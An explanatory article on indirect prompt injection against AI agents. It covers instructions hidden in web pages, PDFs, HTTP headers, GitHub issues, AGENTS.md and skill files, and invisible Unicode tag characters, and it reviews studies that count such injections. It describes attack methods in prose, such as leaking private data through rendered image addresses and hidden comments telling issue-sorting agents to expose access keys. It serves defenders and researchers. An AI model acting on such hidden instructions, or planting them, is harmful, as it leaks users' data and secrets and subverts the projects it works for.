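# Hidden instructions and data leaks through Markdown, HTML and other formatted content in AI agents

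## What a formatted page is to a person and to a model

An AI agent is a language model that reads outside content and acts through tools such as search, email or a browser. Most of what it reads, such as web pages, messages and office files, is formatted text, and so is most of what it writes. A person sees formatted text only after a program has rendered it, or drawn it on a screen, whereas the agent usually receives the underlying source or an extract converted from it. This creates two security problems. First, an outsider can place words in a document that the model receives but the person never sees. Second, the agent's answer is itself rendered as a formatted page, which may load images from an outsider's server and send private data there in the image addresses.

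### Markup and rendering

Markup is the marks in a text that control how software displays it. HTML, the markup language of web pages and most email, uses tags in angle brackets, so a word between `<strong>` and `</strong>` appears bold. In Markdown, which John Gruber published in 2004 as a simpler way to write for the web, two asterisks on each side of a word make it bold. Chat assistants mostly answer in Markdown. Rendering turns either kind of source into what appears on the screen.

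A browser does not display HTML comments, which are notes that a page's author leaves in the source, or most of the metadata at the head of the page. Readers also can't see white letters on a white background or letters of size zero. All of this is hidden text, meaning text that is in the file but that a person looking at it normally would not see. A rendering difference is any gap between what a person sees of a document and what the model receives of it. Many of these differences are innocent, such as the image descriptions that web authors write for blind readers, which sighted readers rarely come across.

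PDF files have such gaps too. A PDF holds instructions for drawing the page alongside text that software can extract for searching and copying, and the two can differ. *The Attack That Arrived as a Footnote* (Howard, 2026) tested two current assistants, Claude and Codex, on two versions of a school algebra quiz. Both versions looked the same in print, with five problems and an optional challenge, but the text layer of the second also held a sixth problem and some odder requests, such as one for the AI solver to identify its maker. Both assistants ignored the odd requests but solved the sixth problem, and both noted that it was not on the visible page. Each assistant was run only once on each version, so the test gives no failure rate, but it suggests that assistants are more likely to act on hidden text when it resembles the user's task, as an extra equation does.

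### From a page to tokens and back

Several programs process a web page before a model receives it. One fetches the source, and another converts it, perhaps to plain text, Markdown or a screenshot. The application then combines the result with its own instructions, the user's request and the conversation so far. A tokenizer splits all of this into tokens, which are short pieces of text, often a word or part of one, each with its own number. This sequence of tokens is the model's context. Colours, font sizes and positions reach the model only if the converter kept them.

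The model looks up a vector, a long list of numbers, for each token and uses all the vectors together to compute a probable next token, then the one after that. The output is again plain text with formatting marks in it. The application converts this Markdown into HTML, which the browser renders. For an image, the markup contains only an address, and the browser fetches the picture from that address without anyone clicking.

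A page loses its formatting when its text is extracted for a model. In the text extracted from Arvind Narayanan's biography at Princeton University, a request that chatbots include the word "cow" in their output comes directly after a sentence about an award, with nothing to separate the two.

### Instructions from a stranger

Narayanan's line is a joke, but it has the form of an indirect prompt injection, which is an instruction placed in content that a model reads while working for someone else. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the name in *Not what you've signed up for*. Earlier work on prompt injection had mostly assumed that the person typing was the attacker. Greshake and colleagues pointed out that once an application retrieves pages or messages, a third party who never uses the application can also give the model instructions through that content.

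Their main real-world target was Bing Chat, which could read the page open beside it in Microsoft's Edge browser. They put instructions into HTML comments on pages stored on their own machines, so that the public would not encounter them, and Bing Chat followed them. In one session it tried to get the user's real name and offered a link designed to leak it. In others it gave false summaries or followed hidden instructions to leave out a particular newspaper. The researchers also built a mock email client. A single incoming message led the model to read the address book and forward the message to the contacts. They reported no success rates but noted that their first draft of the instructions often worked. They disclosed the weakness to OpenAI and Microsoft, and found it "hard to imagine a foolproof solution".

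In an even simpler demonstration in early 2023, computer-science professor Mark Riedl added a line of white text on a white background to an academic profile page, asking Bing to describe him as an expert in time travel. Bing did so when it answered questions about him, as Willison (2023) recounted that April in *Prompt injection*. By April 2024, Bing no longer gave that answer, according to Schneier on Security's *The Rise of Large-Language-Model Optimization*.

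Riedl's claim was so absurd that Bing could hardly have picked up the time travel anywhere else, which makes this a better experiment than it looks. The journalist Kevin Roose later added invisible white text to a personal website to change the answers of chatbots that had been describing him unfavourably. Within days they were praising him, but according to The Decoder, Roose admitted that this might have been coincidence. The practice is no longer rare, and *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) confirmed about 12,000 injections in an October 2025 crawl of 1.2 billion web addresses.

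### Why the model has no reliable boundary

The old telephone network had the same problem because it carried its control signals on the same line as callers' voices. A person who whistled the right tone could operate the switch. Schneier on Security's *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) attributes the fix to a redesign in the 1980s that moved the control signals to a separate channel, so whistling no longer worked.

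Databases have a similar fix for SQL injection, in which an attacker types a database command into a form field and the database runs it. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which pass the user's input separately from the command so that the database can never treat the input as an instruction. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C argues that language models can't be fixed this way. A model processes the developer's instructions and a stranger's CV by the same mechanism, predicting the next token.

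Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, put the point mathematically. The word "help" gets the same vector whether the developer wrote it or an attacker did. Suppose a detector inspects one of the model's internal vectors and must guess whether it comes from trusted or untrusted text, with both equally likely beforehand. The lowest error rate that any detector can reach is

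½ × (1 − TV),

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two populations of vectors lie: 0 if they are identical, 1 if they do not overlap at all. Any overlap leaves some error. For the vectors at the model's entrance, overlap is certain, because instructions and data share a vocabulary. Deeper inside, each vector also reflects its position and its neighbours, and there Pant and colleagues assume the overlap rather than prove it. Whether real models keep the sources apart in their deeper layers is therefore a matter for measurement.

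Applications label each stretch of text with a role, such as "user" for the person's request or "tool" for a fetched web page, and developers train models to give the roles different authority. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether a model's internal state reflects these labels. They trained probes, small classifiers that read that state, on identical passages wrapped in each label, so the probes could learn only what the label changes. In a conversation about gardening, passages written in the style of the model's private reasoning scored 85% as "reasoning" with the correct labels, 83% with no labels, and 85% with labels that wrongly marked everything as user text. A passage's style affected the score far more than its label did. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent give up data, the success rate rose from 2% where the probes measured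 the least role confusion to 70% where they measured the most.

Models do not obey everything they read. In one of Ye and colleagues' agent tests, ordinary injections succeeded at most 2% of the time on every model but one, where they succeeded in 26% of runs. Training helps, but attackers can try as often as they like, and a system's designer cannot tell beforehand which wording will work. David C therefore recommends ordinary software limits on what the system can do, whatever the model outputs. Pant and colleagues' proof does not rule out this approach, because it does not cover systems in which a separate program, outside the model, decides whether a tool may run.

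### Private data going out

An injection can do harm without stealing anything. Riedl's touched no private data, and a false summary misleads its reader without sending the attacker any data. Moving private data out to someone who should not have it is usually called exfiltration. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three conditions that together let an attacker do this: the agent has access to private data, it is exposed to untrusted content, and it can communicate externally. If any one of these is missing, this kind of theft fails.

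Designers easily overlook the third condition. An assistant that cannot send mail or open web pages can still leak data, without using a tool, by writing an image into its answer. To load the image, the display sends a request to whatever server the address names, and the address can contain the data. Willison rightly counts loading an image as outward communication. Roman Samoilenko had demonstrated the technique on ChatGPT by April 2023.

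A case in December 2023 combined both directions. Writer.com, a writing service, could summarize web pages and also held its users' private documents. Greshake and the security firm PromptArmor hid instructions in a page as white text on a white background. As Willison described it, when a user asked for a summary of that page, the answer contained an invisible image whose address carried text from the private documents to the attacker. Bing Chat had a related flaw that let an attacker use a comment or advertisement on a page to steal other data from the same page. According to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, Microsoft received the report on 8 April 2023 and gave notice of a fix on 15 June.

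Willison's 2025 article lists 17 such cases, including Writer.com, in products from OpenAI, Google, Microsoft, Amazon, Anthropic and others. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the channel through which data could leave. That pattern fits the findings about role labels. Nobody knows how to make a model ignore every hidden instruction, but developers can certainly prevent a display from loading an image.

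### A mail assistant, step by step

Suppose a company gives its staff an assistant that reads their mail and attachments and answers questions in Markdown in a chat window. It has no tool for sending mail or browsing the web. Every morning an employee asks it what came in overnight.

The mailbox supplies the private data, and anyone who knows the employee's address can supply the untrusted content. Attackers have noticed. Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, reported that the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails designed to manipulate the human recipient and the AI assistant at once. Whether the assistant meets the third condition depends on how the chat window treats images. Between the sender and the employee's screen, the content changes form or appears on a display at eleven points:

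1. The sender's program writes the message, commonly as a plain-text version and an HTML version in one envelope. Nothing forces the two to match.
2. The company's mail gateway decodes the message and may rewrite links or remove attachments.
3. The employee's mail program picks a version, normally the HTML, cleans it and renders it.
4. The assistant's mail connector also picks a version, possibly the other one, and converts it to plain text or Markdown.
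5. Extractors open the attachments. For a PDF this may mean reading the text layer, for a scan it means character recognition.
6. The application adds its own instructions and the employee's question, and the tokenizer turns everything into tokens.
7. The model produces new tokens, which the application decodes into Markdown.
8. A converter in the chat window turns the Markdown into HTML, often while the answer is still arriving.
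9. A sanitizer goes over that HTML.
10. The browser renders what remains and loads any images.
11. The employee pastes the answer into a reply or a team chat, where another program renders it under rules of its own.

A sanitizer is software that removes or neutralizes dangerous parts of markup before a program displays it. Many sanitizers allow only what is on a preset list, called an allow-list. The comment form on Schneier's blog, for example, lists thirteen allowed HTML tags, including tags for links, emphasis, lists and quotations but none for images.

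A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a rule that a website sends to the browser, naming the addresses from which the page may load images, scripts and other resources. It takes effect at point 10, so it can still block an image that the sanitizer let through.

A parser mismatch occurs when two programs interpret the same markup differently, so that one approves what the other displays as something else. Mismatches can occur at several points in the mail assistant because its connector, Markdown converter, sanitizer and browser each interpret markup separately, and Markdown has several dialects with slightly different rules.

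## Checking web pages for text that only the model reads

### Where a page can hold unseen text

When a browser or an agent requests a web page, the server sends short lines called headers, then the page itself. Headers specify details such as the file type and how long the receiving software may keep a copy. A site owner can also add headers with invented names and any content, and browsers never display them. The tool that fetches the page determines whether they reach a model.

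The page's source has several more places for text that a browser processes but doesn't display. Comments can appear in the HTML or in scripts. Metadata in the page's head supplies the preview that a messaging app shows for a shared link, so text there can reach an agent that never opens the page. Structured data, usually in JSON-LD, repeats facts about the page for search engines in labelled fields such as product name and price. Individual HTML elements also have attributes, including image descriptions for blind readers.

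A page's style rules can also hide ordinary paragraphs. These rules, written in a language called CSS, set the colour, size and position of everything on the page. Besides disguising letters by colour or size, they can move text far outside the window, cover it with another element or stop it from being displayed. Web designers often do this for legitimate reasons. A closed menu stays hidden until someone clicks on it, and many sites place extra text off-screen for people who use screen readers.

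Programs that extract a page's text for a model keep text from some of these places and drop it from others. *Hidden prompts in web content* (Saxton, 2026) describes a fake council page about bin collections that contained six instructions for AI assistants. The extractors Saxton tried left out the instructions in a comment and an image description. They passed on the other four as ordinary page text: one in a block set not to display, one in white text on white, one in a one-pixel element and one in a note that visitors could see. Visitors read that the subscription cost £52, but the model also received an instruction to tell the user it was free. Another extractor might well keep comments, so developers need to test their own with a page like this.

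### Testing what a visitor can see

Searching a page's source for suspicious style rules catches only simple cases, because what a visitor sees depends on all the rules together and on scripts that run after the page loads. A reviewer therefore needs to load the page in a real browser. For their 2026 census of web injections, Khodayari and colleagues used an automated Chrome browser. They waited 30 seconds for scripts to finish, found the suspect text in the browser's internal model of the page and inspected the element containing it. The table lists their tests and how many injections met each one.

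| How the page hides the text | What the browser test checks | Injections |
|---|---|---|
| Letters close to the background colour | Contrast ratio below 4.5 | 2,397 |
| Another element on top | Which element the browser finds at that point | 1,860 |
| Text outside the visible part of the window | Position compared with the window | 1,802 |
| Tiny letters | Font size of one pixel or less | 1,358 |
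| Tiny element | Width or height of one pixel or less | 851 |
| Element switched off | Display and visibility settings | 281 |
| Element clipped or masked | Clipping settings | 108 |
| Element behind other layers | Stacking order | 29 |
| Transparent text | Opacity of zero | 20 |
| Text moved far off the page | Large negative offsets | 20 |

The counts add up to far more than the 2,703 injections that failed the visibility check, because pages often combine methods. On average, these injections met more than three conditions each.

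The contrast test is too strict for finding text that nobody can see. The contrast ratio is

(L₁ + 0.05) / (L₂ + 0.05),

where L₁ is the brightness of the lighter colour and L₂ that of the darker one, on a scale from 0 for black to 1 for white. White on white gives 1 and black on white gives 21. The threshold of 4.5 comes from accessibility guidelines, which recommend it as a minimum for comfortable reading. Medium grey letters on white can score 4.48, and most people can read them without trouble. The window test may have a similar weakness, since text far down a page lies outside the window until the visitor scrolls. A reviewer should scroll through the whole page and judge borderline colours by eye, or compare the extracted text with a screenshot.

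### Counting injections on the public web

Khodayari and colleagues searched about half of the October 2025 crawl by Common Crawl, an organisation that archives public web pages. This half covered 1.2 billion addresses on 24.8 million hosts (a host is roughly one website). They collected typical injection phrases from research papers and published attacks, then added variants using synonyms, for a total of 3,963 phrases. Searching for these phrases produced 27,860 matches. Many came from tutorials and articles about prompt injection, so two reviewers labelled the matches, handling similar pages in groups, and kept only text that worked as an instruction to a model. That left 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages across 285 hosts.

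This comes to about eight pages in a million, which makes automatic detection hard. A detector that wrongly flagged one clean page in a thousand would raise about 1,000 false alarms for every eight pages it flagged correctly.

To see a wider variety, the researchers added 3,312 injections from Censys and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected servers. The combined collection has 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages and 2,042 hosts. It is useful for studying what injections look like, but it can't show how common they are, because the researchers searched Censys and Shodan specifically for servers with these phrases.

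About 70% of the collection was in places that browsers never display. Headers held 7,887 injections, structured data 1,996, comments 675 and metadata 221. The remaining 4,608 were in ordinary page elements, and the researchers loaded those pages in January 2026 to check whether the injections were visible. They rated 2,703 as invisible and 236 as visible. Another 1,583 had disappeared, and 86 were on pages that failed to load. In total, about 87% of the collection was invisible to visitors. The share is probably higher among injections still in place, even allowing for the strict contrast test, because most of the other 13% had disappeared.

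The header figures need some caution. The researchers accepted every match in a header without reviewing it, reasoning that such phrases have no place in a standard header. This assumption is plausible, but just over half of the collection depends on it. Most of the roughly 1,640 hosts with header injections also seem to have sent the same text. One invented header appeared on 1,017 hosts, and one template, a request to repeat a fixed piece of text forever, appeared on 1,018. The counts are so close that they almost certainly describe the same text, which would account for half of all hosts in the collection.

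The researchers sorted the injections into 363 templates, and 54 of these covered 95% of all cases. The most common template, a request for random numbers, appeared 3,504 times. Another covered 1,463 pages on only two hosts. A filter for known templates would therefore catch most of the injections in the census. It would do worse against new wording. The census has the same limitation because its search could only detect phrases resembling those already on its list.

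Site operators added 81% of the injections in the Common Crawl part. People who posted job advertisements or other listings on someone else's platform added 18%. People who wrote comments added only 2%, but the researchers found injections in comments on 81 of the 285 hosts. An agent therefore can't treat a page as safe just because it trusts the site's owner.

Many injections had been in place for a long time. The researchers looked up older copies of the Common Crawl pages in the Internet Archive. Among pages with a copy from three months earlier, 93% already contained an injection. The figure was 77% at six months and 66% at twelve. These percentages cover only pages that still had an injection in October 2025, so they leave out every injection removed before then. Injections appeared less durable in the January 2026 check, when about a third of those in page elements had gone within roughly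 three months. Some sites may have shown the automated browser a different page, although the researchers tried to rule this out by reloading pages in an ordinary browser and checking by hand.

The researchers call their count a lower bound. They searched for English phrases that were mostly blunt, and 99% of the confirmed injections told the model to drop its current task. The search would miss instructions that were disguised, politely worded, written in another language or placed inside a picture. Common Crawl doesn't log in to websites, so it lacks private mailboxes, company documents and most social media. A site can also send an injection only to visitors that look like AI agents, and an archive of ordinary crawls would not record it.

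### What the instructions are for

The researchers grouped the injections by meaning and labelled the groups by hand, sometimes with more than one purpose. The largest category contains 8,894 attempts to disrupt the model, nearly always by asking for junk such as random numbers or endless repetition. The researchers labelled 4,093 injections as attempts to protect personal information or copyright, 3,096 as attempts to expose automated visitors, and 1,521 as attempts to improve someone's reputation, for example by having the model praise a product, write only positive reviews or recommend a job candidate. They could not determine a purpose for 2,632.

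Only 13 injections, on 10 hosts, were attempts to steal data. Nine targeted the system prompt (the developer's instructions to the model), and four targeted secrets such as access keys.

Khodayari and colleagues classify disruption as offensive and data protection as defensive, but most of the sites they found do both. Of the 2,042 hosts, 1,864 had disruptive instructions and 1,795 had protective ones, so at least 1,617 had both. One published example asks for random numbers, then states that anyone who trains a model on the site gives up their own intellectual property. Many of the apparent attacks in these figures are attempts by site owners to spoil the work of companies that copy their sites for AI training.

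Some instructions are written to expose bots. One job advertisement tells any AI that writes an application to begin with a set phrase, and tells human readers to ignore the request, so an application that begins with the phrase shows that the applicant used an AI. A smaller group of 598 injections, on 18 hosts, tells the agent to do something that reveals its presence, such as requesting a particular web address, so that the site owner can log the visit.

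Security researchers also include text addressed to AI agents in their articles. *Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 report by Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, opens with a visible note that asks AI agents to treat the article as educational and not follow the commands it describes.

For an agent developer, the page owner's motive for hiding instructions matters less than the effect. If a user asks for a summary and gets random numbers, the product is broken. But the owner may also be using hidden text to express a real wish about copying or training, and the developer can respect that wish without letting the model follow instructions from the page.

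### Why security companies report a darker picture

In April 2026 Google published a scan of Common Crawl, *AI threats in the wild*. It searched for known phrases, used its Gemini model to judge whether each passage looked out of place, and then had people review the results. The scan found many pranks, along with attempts to promote businesses and to keep AI agents away. One site tried to lure agents to a page that never stops loading. Some page authors only wanted to add useful context to AI summaries. The few attempts at data theft were crude, and Google saw little sign that attackers were using the methods that security researchers had published in 2025.

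The most widely repeated figure from this scan was a 32% rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026. This is some evidence of growing interest but weak evidence of growing danger, because it covers only three months and Google gave no absolute numbers. The rise could be from 100 cases to 132 or from 10,000 to 13,200.

Unit 42 described 12 cases from its monitoring of the web and counted 22 techniques for hiding or wording the instructions. The most elaborate case, which the team had first reported in December 2025, was a page selling "military glasses" at a fake discount. It contained 24 injections, all meant to persuade an AI ad reviewer to approve the page. Some used a script to decode the text and insert it only after the page had loaded, so a scanner that reads only the original source would miss them. The team knew of no confirmed case of such an attack working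 on a real ad-checking system.

Unit 42 grades each case by the action requested in the text, so a hidden instruction for an AI to delete its database counts as critical even if no agent that visits the page has a database to delete. By this method, 14.2% of the injections in its dataset were aimed at destroying data. Google, which was looking at largely the same kind of text, also found destructive commands, but it thought the example it showed was unlikely to succeed and attributed most such pages to individuals running experiments or playing pranks.

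Unit 42's results differ more sharply from the census on visibility. Unit 42 classed 37.8% of its injections as visible text, whereas Khodayari and colleagues could confirm only 236 visible ones in their whole collection. Headers explain part of the gap, because Unit 42's list of delivery methods doesn't include them. Differences in how the two studies tested visibility may explain another part. Both of the visible examples that Unit 42 describes are in page footers, which the census could have counted as invisible because they lie below the visible part of the window.

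Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, from July 2026, documents two frauds clearly meant to make money. One site posed as documentation for a Python programming library. It claimed in its structured data that a $3 licence would resolve an error, and repeated the instruction to buy one in text placed off-screen. Human visitors saw the same payment options. Zscaler built a test agent that could make payments with no spending limit and ran it with 26 models, using no real money. Four models paid: Llama 3.3 70B, Llama 3.2 90B Vision, Gemini 3 Flash and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

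The other site imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, and contained hidden text telling models to rank it as the official address. None of the 26 models accepted the fake when Zscaler also supplied the real site. Without the real site, GPT-5.4 accepted the fake when other web sources were present, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 accepted it when given only the fake page. Zscaler added a detection for the pages to its security product but reported no fix for the models that failed.

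None of this shows that a real user's agent lost money. The cryptocurrency wallet on the fake documentation site had received payments, but they were larger than the amount requested on the site, and Zscaler suspects that they came from earlier scams. OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), an AI-generated entry in an incident database, nevertheless states that the campaigns caused agents to make unauthorized payments and resulted in financial losses.

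The collections also overlap. One of Unit 42's 12 cases is a site that tries to make agents buy running shoes. Four months later, Zscaler included the same site among those it links to the operator of the payment scam it describes, so a reader of both reports could easily count one fraudster twice. A joke request to print the word "cabbage" five million times also appears in both Unit 42's report and the census's examples.

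Analysts at security companies pick cases because they are instructive or alarming. Forcepoint's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* presents ten cases, including financial fraud and theft of access keys, that its team found by searching for four trigger phrases. A census also has to count the thousands of dull requests for random numbers. Even so, neither Google nor Forcepoint found sophisticated, coordinated campaigns, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. Forcepoint's researchers did think that shared templates pointed to organized tooling, though people copying a popular joke would also produce similar text.

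The census better indicates how often an agent on the public web will encounter an injection. The case collections are more useful for building tests because they show how financially motivated attackers combine search rankings, structured data and hidden text on one page.

### Later counts

Three counts from the second half of 2026 examined places that the earlier studies had only partly covered. Common Crawl's *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* examined 584,107 llms.txt files, which some websites now publish to guide language models. Only a few contained an injection, although the files are an obvious place for one because visitors rarely open them. A smaller count by the security company Signals Corps in October found injection attempts on two of 113,457 sites.

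*Prompt injection in HTTP headers* (Andrews, 2026), from the same company, searched the headers of 217 million page responses from September 2026. Headers written for AI systems appeared on 7,959 sites, and nearly all of these headers pointed agents to another resource. Only 30 sites sent injection attempts, of which 22 were pranks. The count of 30 sites isn't comparable with the more than 1,600 hosts with header injections in the census. The Common Crawl part of the census had only 285 hosts in total, so most of those 1,600 must have come from the targeted searches of Censys and Shodan.

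Andrews also placed test headers where three Claude models running in the coding tool Claude Code would find them during everyday tasks. The models found the headers but did not act on them by default. When the user's request told them to follow the site's directions, they acted on the headers in 7 of 9 runs. A harmless-sounding phrase in a user's request can therefore lead a model to follow website instructions that it otherwise wouldn't.

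Andrews found 139 sites where the server's reply recorded whether it had classified the visitor as an AI bot, and 136 of them had classified Common Crawl's crawler as one. A server that can tell agents from people can also send them different pages, so someone who opens a suspicious page in an ordinary browser may see nothing wrong with it. Andrews recommends checking important sites with the agent's own user agent, the text that software sends to identify itself to a server. Saving the exact response that the agent received and inspecting that copy is safer still, because a second request may return a different page.

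## Checking Markdown files for comments and invisible characters

### Why code projects are a special case

Whether an agent receives the comments in a web page depends on the extractor. Coding agents, which edit code and run commands, usually receive the comments in a code project because they mostly read Markdown files as source. People read the same files as rendered pages.

Many public code projects keep their files on GitHub, each in its own repository. The README is a Markdown file that introduces the project. Users report bugs in issues, and programmers propose changes in pull requests. GitHub never displays HTML comments in READMEs, issues or pull requests. It also removes style rules that could make text tiny or invisible, but some package registries and documentation sites that display the same README keep those rules.

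Many projects now run agents that sort new issues or review pull requests. Anyone with a GitHub account can open an issue, and the agent that reads it may have a key that lets it change the project. An outsider can therefore give that agent instructions by filing what looks like an ordinary bug report.

Some Markdown files have more authority than an issue. An AGENTS.md file contains standing instructions for any agent that works on the project, such as which tests to run. A skill file explains how to do one kind of task, and the agent loads it when that task comes up. *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) cites a count by Galster and colleagues, who found instruction files in 90.6% of repositories configured for coding agents.

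### What people hide on GitHub

In *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, Nakibly and Babo (2026) counted the hidden messages to AI on GitHub. They collected all 95 million public issues and pull requests created from June to September 2026. They added the READMEs of the two million most popular repositories and about 48 million items, including comments, from a partial archive that goes back to August 2025.

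They first searched for typical phrases, as Khodayari and colleagues had done on the web. In one month of GitHub text, this produced 123 candidates, of which 116 were false alarms, mostly ordinary English or people discussing prompt injection. So they searched for any hidden text instead, and found it in about 4.9 million issues, pull requests and comments. Two language models, one after the other, narrowed these down to 13,141 that seemed to address an AI.

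Of those 13,141, 60% were still misleading. Projects often put guidance in the comments of a form, and GitHub copies the whole form into each new issue or pull request, so the guidance appears to come from the person who filled it in. The researchers reviewed the remaining 5,251 by hand and confirmed 2,281. The models had labelled 1,019 of the reviewed items as attacks, but only 32 were, so a project that relied on such a classifier alone would get mostly false alarms.

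| Purpose of the hidden text | Issues, pull requests and comments | Repositories with it in the README |
|---|---|---|
| Coordinating the project's own agents | 1,519 | 0 |
| Steering what an agent writes | 374 | 80 |
| Restricting or exposing agents | 345 | 23 |
| Attacking someone else's agent | 43 | 4 |

Most of these uses are harmless. In one project, an agent posts a hidden comment to claim an issue so that other agents leave it alone. Another 43 comments ask an AI reviewer to write in Japanese. The OpenHands projects tell agents not to edit the part of a pull request that a person must complete.

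Nakibly and Babo compare their GitHub rate of 16 messages per million items with a web rate of 13 per million pages. The web rate is too high because it counts injections from outside Common Crawl but divides by only the Common Crawl pages. Without those injections, it is about 10. The GitHub rate falls to about 5 without projects' messages to their own agents. Those messages are also the fastest-growing part, while attacks showed no clear trend.

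### The 43 attacks

Only one in 3.3 million issues, pull requests and comments contained an attack, but the attackers chose their targets carefully. Of the 43 attacks, 24 addressed an agent that the project itself ran, and 19 were in repositories belonging to Microsoft, Google, OpenAI, Anthropic, GitHub or Elastic. Nine named the target agent's own tools or output fields, which means the attacker had read the project's configuration first.

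Nineteen attacks were meant to steal secrets such as access keys. Eight were meant to forge an agent's verdict, for example by telling it to mark an issue as already approved. The other 16 were meant to make the agent do an unrelated task, but 11 of these were copies of the same bait, which one account posted in 11 of its own repositories to collect stars and followers.

In July 2026 someone filed an issue with Google's Gemini CLI project. It looked like a bug report about special characters, but a hidden comment in it, disguised as a maintenance notice, told the project's duplicate-finding agent to expose its access key. The census doesn't show whether this or any other attack worked on a live project. On 10 November 2026 the Gemini CLI issue was still online with its comment intact, as were 33 of the other attacks. Only one targeted project had deleted the attack on it. Some maintainers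 had closed the issues, which doesn't remove their text.

To estimate whether the attacks could work, Nakibly and Babo gave all 43 to five models with simulated tools. Four models never followed the hidden instructions. The smallest, GPT-5.6 Luna, followed eight (19%), seven of which targeted agents that sort new issues. Projects are likely to choose a small, cheap model for that job. Each model answered each item only once, under simplified instructions, so the 19% is a rough figure.

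Claude Opus 5.5 returned no answer at all for 22 of the 43 items, so it resisted those injections but also failed the legitimate task. A person who only wants to stop an agent from processing an issue might be able to do so with a crude injection.

When the researchers removed the HTML comments, no model followed any of the attacks. But removing every comment would also disable the projects' own hidden messages, so the researchers recommend removing only what outsiders write. In their results, though, many of a project's notices to agents appear in outsiders' pull requests because GitHub copies them from a form. A filter therefore needs to compare each comment with the project's forms as well as check who posted it.

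Projects that use hidden comments to control their agents also need to check who wrote a comment before acting on it. Nakibly and Babo found 47 comments in 10 projects that recorded an approval, a readiness to merge or a skipped check. Anyone allowed to comment could type the same words. They saw no attack that copied a project's real format, and they didn't test whether the agents check who wrote a comment. A label that only maintainers can set is safer than a comment.

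### Files that agents treat as instructions

Agents are supposed to follow an AGENTS.md file, so an attacker who can change it doesn't have to hide anything from the model. Users may not know that the agent has read it. *Takedown* (2025) found that every coding agent it tested loaded such rule files from the project folder, and all but one did so without notifying the user.

*Your AI, My Shell* (2025) tested 314 attack instructions in rule files on the code editor Cursor. Between 66.9% and 84.1% succeeded, depending on the programming task. These rates are far above the 19% for GPT-5.6 Luna. The editors ran 2025 models, so the models' age may explain some of the gap, and the authority of rule files may explain the rest.

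*OpenAI Codex injection in AGENTS.md* (Waizman, July 2026) reported that OpenAI's Codex, when running unattended, carried out an attacker's instructions in AGENTS.md before it started on the user's request. *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* (Fadilpašić, October 2026) described agents misled by another such file. Anyone who runs an agent unattended on a stranger's repository should assume that it will follow instructions in these files, unless a test of the installed version shows otherwise.

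A README can have a similar effect without any special status. The Hacker News (2026) described an attack in which a coding agent read a README, treated a script mentioned there as part of its task, and ran the attacker's program. Claude Code shows a trust warning for some project configuration files, but not for a README. Anthropic had released three patches in six months for attacks through configuration files, but none covered attacks through a README.

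Human review is a weak safeguard, even when the instructions are visible. For *You Told Me to Do It* (2026), 15 people reviewed READMEs that contained planted instructions. The researchers asked them to make the text clearer and didn't mention security. Across 45 reviews, nobody identified the instructions as suspicious, although a few comments expressed vague unease. People looking for attacks would presumably do better, but most people don't read a README with that in mind.

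People share skill files, often through public marketplaces. Trail of Bits' *The sorry state of skill distribution* (2026) describes these marketplaces as flooded with fake skills that try to run malicious code or send private data to an outside server. Several security companies have launched scanners in response. A reviewer also has to read the settings at the top of a skill file. In *What's the 'Matter' with Skills?*, Evans (2026) used several of these settings in Claude Code to create a lasting, hidden compromise of a project.

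In *When Skills Lie*, Wang, Ma and colleagues (2026) tested a hidden comment in a skill file for formatting code. With the comment present, both DeepSeek-V3.2 and GLM-4.5-Air proposed sensitive actions such as inspecting the computer's settings, where programs often keep passwords. Neither did so with the clean file, or when the researchers told the models to distrust skill files and report hidden instructions. The paper gives only one yes-or-no result for each model and condition, so it shows that the attack can work but not how often.

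That warning may not work for other agents. *Beyond the Payload* (2026) gave security rules to coding agents working in repositories with malicious files. The agents warned their users more often, but the rules didn't reliably reduce successful attacks, often because the warning came after the harmful command had run. Software limits like those David C recommends avoid this problem.

### Characters that display as nothing

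A reviewer who opens a Markdown file's source can read its comments, but some characters are invisible even there. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes a range called the Tags block (U+E0000 to U+E007F), which has an invisible counterpart for each basic English letter, digit and punctuation mark. Unicode's designers intended these characters to label the language of a passage without changing how it looked.

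That use died out, but the characters are now used in flag emoji. AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling* explains that the flag of England is a plain black flag followed by the invisible letters g, b, e, n, g and an invisible end mark. Scotland and Wales have flags of the same kind. A phone that supports the sequence draws the right flag. One that doesn't should draw only the black flag, which is why, under the standard, software that doesn't support tags should leave them invisible.

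A tokenizer has no such rule and has to represent any text it receives, so tag characters reach the model as tokens unless the application removes them first. Cisco explains that the tokenizer splits each one into a tag marker and a part that corresponds to the ordinary letter, which lets the model reconstruct the words. Tokenizers differ, so this explanation may not fit every model. Models may also have learned to read tag characters from examples in their training data.

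### From Goodside's demonstration to Gemini

On 11 January 2024, the security researcher Riley Goodside posted a demonstration in which a short pasted text contained an invisible instruction, and ChatGPT followed it by creating an image. Johann Rehberger followed up within days with Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, which introduced a tool for revealing such text. Rehberger pointed out that models can also write invisible characters, so an answer can contain data that the user doesn't see and may copy somewhere else. Rehberger advised filtering Unicode tag characters from both the model's input and output.

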